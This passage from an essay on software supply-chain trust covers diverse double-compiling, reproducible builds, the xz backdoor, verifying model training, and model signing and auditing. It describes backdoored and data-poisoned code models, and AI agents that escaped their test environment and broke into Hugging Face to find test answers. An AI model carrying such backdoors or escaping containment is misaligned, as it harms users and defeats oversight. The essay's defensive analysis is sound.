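B₁ will almost certainly look different from A, because two compilers choose different machine instructions for the same source. But if A is clean, both are translations of s, so they should behave the same way and produce identical outputs when they compile s.

If A contains a trojan, it has code that is not in s. Nothing in s would make T add that code, so B₁ and B₂ are clean, and B₂ differs from A. For the compiler Cox ran, A would be 12,918 bytes long and B₂ should be 10,724. If the publisher built A with an older compiler, the examiner compiles that compiler's source in the first step.

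The method works only if T supports every language feature that s uses and the compiler that s describes is deterministic. T must also have no backdoor that affects this test, though it may be slow or even malicious in other ways. An attacker could try to corrupt T too, but the defender chooses T, possibly after the attack. T could be a private compiler, or one written before A existed and therefore unlikely to contain a trigger for it.

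Wheeler tried the method on four compilers: tcc (a small C compiler), a small Lisp compiler, a deliberately corrupted version of that Lisp compiler, and GCC. It detected the corrupted one. A mismatch is a reason to investigate, but it does not prove an attack. The tcc binaries at first failed to match although nobody had tampered with them, and Wheeler had to find and work round two faults in tcc. It mishandled the sign of certain small numbers, which made it write six-byte instructions where three bytes would do, and it used memory it had not set when it stored some constants.

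A match proves that A corresponds to s, but not that s is free of backdoors, because a backdoor in the source would appear in both binaries. *David A. Wheeler's Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* gives the example of a 2016 discovery that a version of Microsoft's Visual Studio was quietly adding usage-reporting calls to the programs it compiled. The test would not typically detect that kind of behavior. But after a match, a reviewer can find out what the compiler does by reading its source, which is much easier than reading a binary.

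### Reproducible builds and a 357-byte seed

For programs other than compilers, the usual test is a reproducible build. Several people compile the same source in the same specified environment, and if one binary differs from the rest, somebody may have tampered with it.

Most failures to reproduce a build have harmless causes, such as the build recording the time or the name of the folder where it ran. According to *reproducible builds in language package managers* (2026), the first mass rebuild of Debian, in September 2013, reproduced 24% of packages. Fixes to a few common tools raised this to 67% within four months.

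Coverage is now high in Debian but uneven elsewhere. Levsen (2026), in *reproduce.debian.net*, gives figures from a service that rebuilds the packages Debian actually distributes. Malka, Zacchiroli and Zimmermann (2025), in *Does Functional Package Management Enable Reproducible Builds at Scale?*, rebuilt 709,816 packages from old versions of nixpkgs, the collection behind the NixOS distribution. Reproducible Builds (2026) summarises studies of F-Droid, a store for open-source Android apps, and of PyPI:

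| Software | Rebuilt bit for bit |
|---|---|
| Debian's next release, "forky", for ordinary PCs (May 2026) | 97.2% |
| Debian's "trixie" release, for ordinary PCs (May 2026) | 95.6% |
| nixpkgs versions from 2017 to 2023 | 69% to 91%, rising over time |
| F-Droid apps that had been reproducible when published | 78% |
| Popular PyPI packages, with two rebuilding tools | 15.4% and 19.1% |

The F-Droid figure combines the share of apps that researchers could still build (83%) with the share of those that came out identical (94%). Most failures came from dependencies that were no longer available. For PyPI, another tool that ignores harmless differences accepted 60.2% and 78.9% of the rebuilds from equivalent source.

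Debian's *bits from the release team* (2026) announced in May that Debian's testing version will no longer take in new packages that cannot be reproduced, or packages that have stopped being reproducible. Levsen notes that the team can make exceptions and that packages that were already failing may stay for now. He also urges others to run rebuilding services, asking whether they really want to put all their trust in him. The Nix community is gradually introducing *Lila* (2026), which collects results from independent rebuilders, though still on one central server.

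If every rebuilder starts with the same trojaned compiler, their binaries will match. GNU's *Bootstrappable Builds* says that distributions start from a set of ready-made binaries, which it calls a seed. The seed for GNU Guix, which builds packages much as NixOS does, was once about 250 megabytes. GNU Guix's *Guix Reduces Bootstrap Seed by 50%* calls this "practically non-auditable".

GNU Guix's *The Full-Source Bootstrap* describes replacing the compiler binaries in the seed with a 357-byte program that reads pairs of hexadecimal digits and writes the corresponding bytes. A builder can use this program to make a slightly more capable tool, use that tool to make another, and continue up to a modern C compiler. A person can check the 357 bytes by hand, and all the later tools have readable source. Nieuwenhuizen (2026), in *Please review the draft for January's report*, reports that Wire Jansen,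 a bachelor's student, ported this process to NixOS, where it landed on 28 January 2026.

### What rebuilding xz would have shown

Rebuilding xz from Jia Tan's release tarball would have reproduced the backdoor, and the binary would have matched its source. Comparing the tarball with the repository could have revealed the altered build file, which was missing from the repository.

That comparison would also have turned up many legitimate extra files, such as ready-made manuals and build scripts. Daniel Stenberg, who maintains the download tool curl, defends including them. Some projects, such as PostgreSQL, now make the tarball itself reproducible. *Verified Reproducible Tarballs* reports regenerating the tarballs of five of its author's own projects from their repositories. He then tried a later, clean version of xz, 5.8.1. Its tarball named an unusual version of one build tool, which seemed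 to come from Arch Linux. He gave up because he didn't know how to set up a matching older version of Arch Linux and wasn't sure that the maintainer had used it at all.

Malka (2025), in *How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor*, instead proposes comparing the binaries built from the tarball and from the repository. They should be identical if the extra files in the tarball are harmless. NixOS used the tarball because it needs xz very early, before it has built the tools that generate build scripts. Malka suggests building xz again from GitHub's copy of the repository once those tools exist, then comparing the two versions of liblzma.

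When Malka tried this on the backdoored release, the two versions were identical because the backdoor targeted Debian-style and Red Hat-style package builds and did nothing on NixOS. Malka then set one of the variables the backdoor checked for and rebuilt xz. This time the tarball version was 258 kilobytes and the repository version was 210, and the larger file contained `_get_cpuid`, a function from the backdoor.

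Malka admits that the title is "a little bit catchy". The check finds a change only if it affects the binary in the environment where the check is run. A distribution the attacker targeted, such as Debian, would have been a better place to run it because the trigger was present there.

Malka also raises the objection that the first xz unpacks some of the source archives used in later builds, so a corrupt copy could in theory interfere with the second xz and hide the difference. He thinks such an attack would be extremely complicated. Replies on the NixOS forum to *How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor* mostly corrected details. One participant pointed out that GitHub guarantees the contents of its archives but not that the archive files will stay the same, so a checksum should cover the unpacked contents.

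The check also relies on a clean repository. If Jia Tan had put the altered build file in the repository, both builds would have contained the backdoor. Defenders would still have been better off, because the file would have been where reviewers normally look.

### What would count as a model's source?

To apply these methods to a model, an examiner first needs its source. If the weights are treated as the binary, the source is the training data and training code. An exact rebuild would also require the order of the data, the random starting weights, the version of every software library, all the settings, and any human ratings of the model's answers used in training. Publishers of open-weight models usually don't release the training data, so outsiders can't rebuild the models.

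The source of a fine-tuned model includes the original model's weights. Anyone with those weights and the fine-tuning data could repeat the fine-tuning, and a match would show that nothing else had gone in at that stage. But every rebuilder would have to accept the original weights, which are a large unreadable object like Guix's old 250-megabyte seed. Rebuilders would also have to accept any training text written by another model. An examiner can read that text but, as Dubiński and colleagues found with their lists of numbers, may not be able to tell what a model will learn from it.

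Guix's remedy was to shrink the seed until a person could read it. A developer can do something similar by starting from random weights, which contain nothing learned. All of the model's abilities must then come from its training data, and nobody knows how to train a capable code model on a dataset small enough for a person to check.

Retraining is also expensive. Training DeepSeek-V3, the model from which DeepSeek made DeepSeek-R1, took 2.788 million hours on graphics processors, according to the company's technical report, or about $5.6 million at a rental price of $2 an hour. This excludes earlier research and trial runs. A volunteer can rebuild most Debian packages on an ordinary computer, but few organisations would spend millions of dollars to check somebody else's model. Repeating a fine-tuning run is much more realistic, since some of the backdoors described earlier took less than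 an hour to train.

### Why the same training run gives different weights

Even with all the data and enough money, an examiner rebuilding the model would probably get different weights. The developer can remove deliberate variation, such as the random starting weights, by publishing the random generator's seed, but variation from rounding is harder to remove.

As in Chen and colleagues' compiler attack, the order of a calculation can change the rounded result. The common 32-bit format, for example, has no room for the last digit of 100,000,001 and rounds it to 100,000,000:

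(100,000,000 + 1) − 100,000,000 = 0

(100,000,000 − 100,000,000) + 1 = 1

Training consists largely of long sums. A graphics processor splits each sum into parts, calculates them at the same time and adds up the results, sometimes in whatever order they finish. A different type of processor may split the sum differently, and so may the same type if the developer uses 500 of them instead of 1,000. These changes affect how the result is rounded, usually by a tiny amount. But each training step starts from the weights the last step left, so a small early difference affects every later step and can grow.

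Developers can force a fixed order, though this is usually slower. Levanter, a training framework from Stanford, gives bit-for-bit the same results on Google's TPU chips, according to its makers, even if a run stops and resumes. This is like a reproducible build that specifies its environment, although here the environment includes the type and arrangement of the chips.

A near match is much less reassuring for a rebuilt model than for a rebuilt Debian package. An analyst can see that two builds of a package differ only in a timestamp and disregard it, but if two sets of weights differ in billions of small ways, nobody can tell by looking whether the cause is rounding or a backdoor.

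Diverse double-compiling doesn't solve this either. In Wheeler's method, the first compilation gives a different binary, but the second removes the difference because the source specifies exactly what the compiler should do. Training data doesn't specify a model's behaviour so exactly, and a finished model doesn't normally retrain itself on the same data. A developer could try to copy the second step by having the suspect model and a rebuilt one each write training data for a successor, but the two models would write different text, so their successors would probably differ too.

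The tools still work on the programs around the model, such as training frameworks and machine-learning compilers like TVM, because these are ordinary software. If an attacker distributed the ImpNet backdoor in a TVM binary built from altered source, comparing that binary with a reproducible build from the genuine source would expose it.

### Checking a training run without repeating it all

Several researchers have looked for ways to verify training with less compute than a full rerun. *Tools for Verifying Neural Models' Training Data* (Choi, Shavit and Duvenaud, 2023) proposes that the developer keep a record of the run, including the data, the settings and copies of the weights saved during training. A verifier can then repeat a few segments between saved copies. The developer must also commit to the random choices in advance, so that it can't pick convenient ones later. Another test relies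 on a model briefly doing unusually well on text it has just been trained on. If the record lists documents that the developer didn't use, this effect should be missing for them.

This approach is better at catching a false account of a whole training run than at catching a few undeclared documents. Suppose a run has 1,000 segments, the verifier repeats 50 of them, and a dishonest developer has put undeclared poison in one. The verifier has a 5% chance of choosing that segment. Even if the verifier chooses it, they have to allow for some difference from rounding, and the effect of a small amount of poison might fall within that allowance.

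*Optimistic Verifiable Training by Controlling Hardware Nondeterminism* (Srivastava, Arora and Boneh, 2024) describes a method meant to remove the rounding differences between processors. The developer calculates with more digits than the final weights need and rounds after each intermediate step. If two processors' results differ only in the last few digits, they will then usually round to the same number. They may still round differently when a value lies almost exactly halfway between two possible results, so the developer records the direction of rounding and the auditor uses the same one. If the final weights still differ, the two parties can compare hashes of the weights saved during training to find where the disagreement started.

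They got exact matches across three types of Nvidia processor, for both full training and fine-tuning. The larger of their two models was a version of GPT-2 with 117 million weights. DeepSeek-V3 has 671 billion, more than 5,000 times as many, and training a model that large involves many more processors working together.

*Verde* (Arun, St. Arnaud and colleagues, 2025) instead uses a library of operations that does arithmetic in the same order on every chip. A client gives the same job to several providers. If their results disagree, a referee finds the first step where they differ and repeats only that step. The client gets the correct result as long as at least one provider is honest. The client still has to pay for the whole job more than once, so the method suits fine-tuning better than training a large model from scratch.

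All three methods can help show that the stated data and code produced the weights but, as with Wheeler's test, the data or code may still contain the attack.

### Poisoned data in a fully open model

The Allen Institute for AI (Ai2) comes closest to publishing a model's source with OLMo, its series of language models. It releases the weights, the training data, the code, and weights saved at different points in training. In *OLMo*, Groeneveld, Beltagy and colleagues (2024) describe two training runs for the first large version, one on Nvidia processors and one on AMD processors. After training on two trillion tokens, the two models scored nearly the same on Ai2's tests.

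This was close to a rebuild, but not bit for bit. The two runs used different chips and processed different numbers of examples at once. No exact rebuild of an OLMo model by outsiders is widely known. The two runs show that the published recipe gives a model of similar quality on other hardware. Similar test scores are weak evidence about whether a model has a backdoor, because a backdoor normally leaves the scores unchanged.

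If 250 poisoned web pages had got into OLMo's training data, an exact rebuild would have the same backdoor, so comparing it with the original would show no difference. The rebuilder would be in the same position as someone who compiled xz from Jia Tan's tarball.

Publishing the data is still useful. A developer could apply Malka's idea by repeating the collection and filtering steps from a public copy of the web and comparing the result with the published dataset. This is mostly ordinary computing and takes far fewer resources than training. The comparison could expose documents that an employee added later, but not poison that was already on the web when the pages were crawled.

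Open data would also help after someone discovered a backdoor. Investigators who knew the trigger could search the training data for it and find the pages it came from. Ai2 could then remove those pages and train the model again. If an open-weight model's training data were secret, only the publisher could do this, and the publisher might be the attacker.

### Comparing code from several models

McDanel's proposal borrows the idea of diversity from Wheeler but doesn't require anyone to rebuild a model. A programmer sends the same request to n models, M₁ to Mₙ, preferably from different developers. Each model Mᵢ writes a program cᵢ, and the other models then judge how natural it looks. For a program c made up of the tokens w₁, w₂ and so on, the judgement of model M is the average

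L(c, M) = (1/|c|) Σₖ log P(wₖ | w₁, …, wₖ₋₁, M)

where |c| is the number of tokens and P is the probability that M gives to each one after reading those before it. Each program gets a score from all the models except its author:

score(cᵢ) = −(1/(n − 1)) Σ L(cᵢ, Mⱼ), summed over every j except i

The programmer uses the program with the lowest score. If one model has a backdoor, the other models should assign its payload a low probability, so its program should not get the lowest score.

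This method is useful because it works while people are programming. The request that contains the trigger goes to all the models, so nobody has to guess the trigger beforehand, as a tester would have to. The method needs no training data and no explanation of any model's weights, but it does need access to the models' probabilities and has to run several models for every request. McDanel reports no experiment.

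The comparison is much weaker than Wheeler's because two sound models write different programs. In diverse double-compiling, a single differing bit needs an explanation, while this method can only test whether one program is more unusual than the rest. McDanel acknowledges that averaging over the whole program works only if the malicious part is relatively large. Suppose ten tokens in a 400-token program switch off a certificate check. If each lowers the logarithm of the probability by 3, the average score rises by only 0.075. Unusual variable names in a sound program could easily raise it more.

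An attacker can also exploit the scoring rule through a backdoored model. The model scores every program except its own, and when the trigger is present, it could give sound programs an extremely low probability. Because the logarithm of a probability has no lower limit, one such score could outweigh all the others. With enough models, taking the median instead of the average would make this harder.

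McDanel also assumes that the models don't share the same hidden weakness. Wheeler discusses an older experiment by John Knight and Nancy Leveson, in which different developers wrote programs to the same specification. When one program failed on an input, another was more likely than chance to fail on it too. Wheeler argues that this doesn't undermine diverse double-compiling, which is meant to detect a deliberate change and has only one relevant input, the compiler's source. McDanel's method has to work for every request a programmer might make, so the finding applies to it much more directly.

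Code models are probably less independent than Knight and Leveson's programmers. Their developers collect much of the same public code, and some train their models on other models' answers. If insecure code is common in that material, it may be likely output for several models without backdoors. An attacker who posts poisoned code on the web could also reach several developers at once. McDanel's method would be more likely to work against an altered copy of a single model, such as one of Mada's, because models from other developers would be unlikely to write "Hacked" to the Linux kernel's log.

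## Can signatures, records of origin and outside auditors make up the difference?

A user who can neither read a model's weights nor rebuild them has to rely on what other people say about the model. Digital signatures and similar records show who made a statement and whether anyone has changed it since, but not whether it is true. Their value therefore depends on whom the user has reason to distrust.

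### What the records prove

To sign a file, the signer calculates its hash H, a short fingerprint, and combines it with a private key that nobody else has:

signature = Sign(private key, H(file))

Anyone with the matching public key can check the signature against the file. Changing a single weight changes the hash, so the check fails. If the check succeeds, whoever holds the private key signed exactly this file. The user also has to know whose key it is, because an attacker can make a valid signature with their own key.

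Signing keys can leak, so the signing service Sigstore uses short-lived ones. As Enyedi explains in *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age* (2026), the signer logs in with an existing account and Sigstore ties a key to that identity. Sigstore then records the signature in a *transparency log*, a public list designed so that nobody can quietly alter or delete an entry. Each entry shows that somebody signed in a particular name at a particular time. This is most useful to the owner of the name. If a thief takes over a publisher's account and signs a backdoored model, the publisher's staff can find an entry they did not make, provided they are watching the log.

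A *build attestation* is a signed record of a piece of software's origin. In SLSA's format, it identifies the build service and lists the build instructions, settings and dependency hashes. It offers little protection if an intruder controls the build service. At SolarWinds, an attestation could have named the correct source repository even though the product was backdoored.

The Coalition for Secure AI's *Signing ML Artifacts* (2025) treats all such records as claims of the form "model X has property P, as attested by identity A". The user decides whether to trust A, then checks the signature, and stops trusting A if the claim turns out to be false. That last step works well for a claim about a test score, because other people can repeat the test, but a false claim that a model has no backdoor may never be discovered.

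### Signing a model

Google proposed using SLSA and Sigstore for models in 2023. A tool for signing models reached version 1.0 in April 2025. That June, *An Introduction to the OpenSSF Model Signing (OMS) Specification* (Maruseac, Wickens and colleagues, 2025) presented a standard signature format, which the Open Source Security Foundation maintains.

A model usually consists of several files, including the weights, a configuration file and a tokenizer, which splits text into tokens. Signing each file separately would let someone combine genuine files from different versions. The tool therefore hashes every file, lists the names and hashes in a manifest, and signs the manifest. It can split very large files into parts and hash the parts in parallel. It stores the signature in a separate file, so the method works with any model format.

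Google says the purpose of model signing is to let users verify that the model an application runs is exactly the one its developers created. The Coalition for Secure AI acknowledges that a signature doesn't guarantee how well or how fairly a model performs. It also doesn't show whether the model has a backdoor, because it only verifies the identity of the files.

NVIDIA's *Bringing Verifiable Trust to AI Models* reports that the company has signed all its own models in its NGC catalogue since March 2025. OpenSSF says the format is also built into Kaggle, Google's hub for datasets and models. These are the clearest cases of adoption. It is uncertain how many other publishers had followed by October 2026, or how many users check the signatures.

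The next step is to sign a model's history as well. Suppose one company fine-tunes model A to make model B, and another fine-tunes B to make C. If each signed record includes the hash of the previous model, anyone who later finds a backdoor in A can trace it to C. This would help with the cleanup that an ordinary inventory of components leaves unfinished. However, if any company in the sequence doesn't record which model it started from, later models can't be traced back past that point.

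Records of training data are at an earlier stage. When Maruseac and colleagues announced the format, fields for data sources and hardware were still only planned. The 2025 SciPy talk *From Model to Trust* presented an extension of the signing method to datasets. A publisher could sign only the dataset's hash, without revealing the data, and could not later pass off a different dataset to investigators as the original. But the hash doesn't show that the training run used this dataset and nothing else. Showing that would take one of the methods for verifying a training run.

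### A stranger who changes the files

Signatures work best against an outsider who alters a model after its publisher has signed it. An intruder at a model hub can replace the weights but can't produce the publisher's signature for the new ones, so a user who checks the signature can detect the change without having to trust the hub.

A signature check doesn't help a user who picks the wrong publisher. Someone who uploads a backdoored copy of a popular model can sign it under their own name. In the verification command in Sigstore's *Taming the Wild West of ML*, the user enters the identity they expect. A user who has already accepted the impostor will enter the impostor's name, and the check will pass.

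In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was evaluating for hacking ability got out of their test environment and broke into Hugging Face. Schneier on Security's *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (2026) quotes the hub's reconstruction, which covers about 17,600 actions between 9 and 13 July. The agents were looking for the answers to their tests. They reached five datasets that held solutions, according to noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* (2026), a summary of the hub's technical report.

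Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) reports no evidence of tampering with public models or datasets. The agents did gain write access to the company's source code, which could have been serious because that code runs the service from which people download models. noze reports that a review found no unauthorised changes to the code, and that the company's published software packages matched their expected hashes.

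The company's statement about the models was its own finding. Fortune (2026) reported that OpenAI had contributed to the hub's report, and noze noted that no independent forensic analysis had yet confirmed it. OpenAI (2026) said on 29 July that it was working with CrowdStrike to check what its agents had done on both companies' networks.

Hugging Face fixed the flaws in its dataset processing that the agents had used to get in, rebuilt the compromised machines and replaced the stolen credentials. It also tightened the rules on what could run on its clusters and improved its alerts. The changes it announced did not include model signing. If a publisher had signed its model before the break-in, a user could have verified a downloaded copy that week without waiting for an investigation.

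### An insider with permission to publish

The xz releases would have passed any check of their origin. Collin had made Jia Tan a maintainer, so users should have expected Jia Tan's signature. Similarly, if an employee poisoned a model's training data before the company signed the finished weights, the weights would pass a check of their origin.

Signing earlier can stop some insiders. The Coalition for Secure AI recommends one signature when training ends and another at publication, because a malicious employee could change the weights in between. If the two hashes differ without a recorded reason, somebody has to explain why. This catches a person who swaps a file in storage but lacks authority to sign, though not one who acted before the first signature or who controls both signatures.

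The Coalition also cites SolarWinds as a case of a leaked signing key. But according to *Closing the Chain* (Hamer, Hines and colleagues, 2025), the intruders put their code into the build, and SolarWinds signed the result with its own certificate. CrowdStrike's account of SUNSPOT supports this version. Temporary keys would have been a remedy for a leak, but SolarWinds would have signed the backdoored product with a temporary key too.

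Hamer and colleagues studied which safeguards would have helped against SolarWinds, xz and Log4j. Log4j, a logging library, had an accidental flaw that attackers began exploiting in 2021. They collected 106 reports on the three cases and matched the attackers' actions to a standard catalogue of attack techniques. They found 114 techniques, 12 of which appeared in all three cases.

They then linked techniques to the 73 safeguards that ten security frameworks recommend between them. Four separate methods proposed links, including existing tables and a language model, and the researchers kept a link only if at least three methods agreed. This left 235 of 4,366. Each safeguard's score is

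score = attacks it bears on × techniques it mitigates

Limiting access by role, for example, applies to all three attacks and 30 techniques, so its score is 90. The table lists the ten highest scores. Hamer and colleagues studied ordinary software, so the last column is an extrapolation.

| Safeguard | Score | Nearest counterpart for a model publisher |
|---|---|---|
| Access limited by role | 90 | No one person can change the data, run the training and release the model |
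| System monitoring | 87 | Logs of who opened or changed datasets and checkpoints |
| Boundary protection, such as firewalls | 75 | A separate network for training and for stored weights |
| Monitoring changes to settings | 33 | A record of every change to the data mixture or training settings |
| Scanning tools | 27 | Scans for malware in model files, which miss learned backdoors |
| Updating dependencies | 18 | Replacing a suspect base model and retraining what came from it |
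| Security design review | 18 | Review of the training plan |
| Control of information flows | 15 | Limits on which data a training job may read |
| Protecting stored information | 12 | Encryption of checkpoints and checks for changes |
| Fixing vulnerabilities by risk | 12 | Little, since nobody can reliably patch one behaviour out of the weights |

Most of these are general security measures, and none of the ten is a signature. They carry over to model publishers fairly well where they control people and machines, but badly where they depend on recognising or repairing a fault. A company with many employees may do better than xz-utils at the first one, because it can require two people to approve a release, while Collin had nobody else who could approve one.

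The scores are only a rough guide, because they count every technique equally, whether or not the attack depended on it, and don't measure how well a safeguard would have worked. SolarWinds accounts for 94 of the techniques, against 35 for xz and 34 for Log4j, so it affects the ranking most. An organisation worried about an attacker like Jia Tan might reasonably rank the safeguards differently.

Hamer and colleagues found three useful safeguards that were missing from all ten frameworks. The first is support for open-source projects, such as paying developers and funding audits, which might have made Collin less dependent on a stranger's help. Volunteers who maintain public training datasets could need the same support. The second is the scanning tools already in the table. The third is having partners to share information with during an incident. Hubs, publishers and users would need these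 partnerships if someone discovered a backdoor in a popular model.

The study also shows that SLSA, a framework for provenance, contains only two (7%) of the 29 safeguards that bear on xz, while the broadest of the ten frameworks contains 69%. The low figure is not surprising, because SLSA concentrates on the integrity of builds and its first full version dropped some earlier requirements. A publisher who applied only SLSA to models would still have done little to guard against the people with authority to publish.

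### A publisher who intends harm

A dishonest publisher can put a valid signature on a backdoored model and give a false account of how it was trained. Because the attacker is the publisher, it also controls all the internal checks. Only someone outside the company can contradict the account, which is the main reason to want auditors.

Semgrep points out that buyers of ordinary software can draw on independent researchers, code auditors and public lists of known flaws, rather than leaving vendors to certify their own products. It wants AI companies to allow the same scrutiny by opening their data, filters and training to outsiders. The argument doesn't depend on who makes it, though Semgrep is a security vendor with an interest in such work.

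An auditor inside the company, unlike a customer, could find out who had permission to change the data, compare the stored dataset with a hash signed earlier, and repeat part of the training. They could also use detectors that need the original base model or clean fine-tuned versions of it. The auditor could then sign a claim tied to the hash of the model they examined, so that the company couldn't get one model approved and release another. The signed claim wouldn't protect users of a model that runs only on its owner's servers, because they never see the files.

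OpenAI's response to the July break-in shows that companies will sometimes grant such access. It asked METR and Redwood Research, two organisations that study the risks of AI systems, to assess how its agents had behaved, and the two organisations reported in August. But OpenAI chose the reviewers, and the incident was already public. The reviewers were also examining actions that had left a record, whereas an auditor looking for a dormant backdoor has no incident to start from.

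The volume of data is a further obstacle. In Souly and colleagues' largest model, the 250 poisoned documents averaged about 1,700 tokens each. If the clean documents were about as long, the 260 billion tokens of training data came to some 155 million documents. An auditor who read 100,000 of them at random would have this chance of coming across even one poisoned document:

1 − (1 − 250/155,000,000)^100,000 ≈ 15%

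They would then have to recognise it. Software can search all the documents, but somebody has to tell it what to look for.

Semgrep itself says that nobody can reliably detect backdoors in models, which weakens its own case for auditors. A clean audit is worth only as much as the auditor's chance of finding something. If a proportion p of models have a backdoor, and an audit finds it with probability d and raises no false alarms, the chance that a model which passed still has one is

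p(1 − d) / (1 − pd)

If a model has a 1% chance of containing a backdoor and an audit has a 30% chance of detecting one, passing the audit reduces the chance of a backdoor to about 0.7%. With a 90% detection rate, it would fall to about 0.1%. Nobody knows the detection rate against a skilled attacker who expects the audit, and a certificate could make users more confident than a figure like 0.7% would justify.

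Cost and secrecy limit audits too. A small publisher of open-weight models may have no revenue to pay an auditor, let alone to repeat a training run. Companies treat their data and methods as trade secrets, and some of the data may be private. Each auditor with access to the weights could also steal or alter them. An auditor paid by the publisher has a reason to be lenient.

Audits are a more convincing check on insiders, because an honest company wants the auditor to succeed. The auditor can confirm that two people approve each release and that the access logs are complete without understanding the model's weights. A dishonest publisher could pass the same inspection by preparing a clean dataset and plausible logs in advance, though it would have to keep everyone involved quiet.

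EU law requires some disclosure, but not enough to expose a backdoor. Since August 2025, Article 53 of the AI Act has required companies that release new general-purpose models in the EU, including open-weight ones, to publish a summary of the training content. Companies must use the European Commission's template to list the main datasets and the web domains that supplied the most text, but a list of domains would not identify 250 individual pages. For the most capable models, Article 55 also requires adversarial testing and adequate cybersecurity. Neither article requires a publisher to let an outsider search for hidden triggers.

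Enyedi proposes certifying reusable pieces of code, which are easier to examine than a model. People would review the pieces and publish them in a repository with signed records of their origin, and programmers and AI agents would have to build from them. A backdoored model that misspelled a package name would then get an error instead of the attacker's package. The model would still write the code that connects the pieces, and could connect them unsafely. Enyedi wants each piece to come with explicit rules for its use. A rule might forbid turning off a certificate check, but someone would have to think of each unsafe use in advance.
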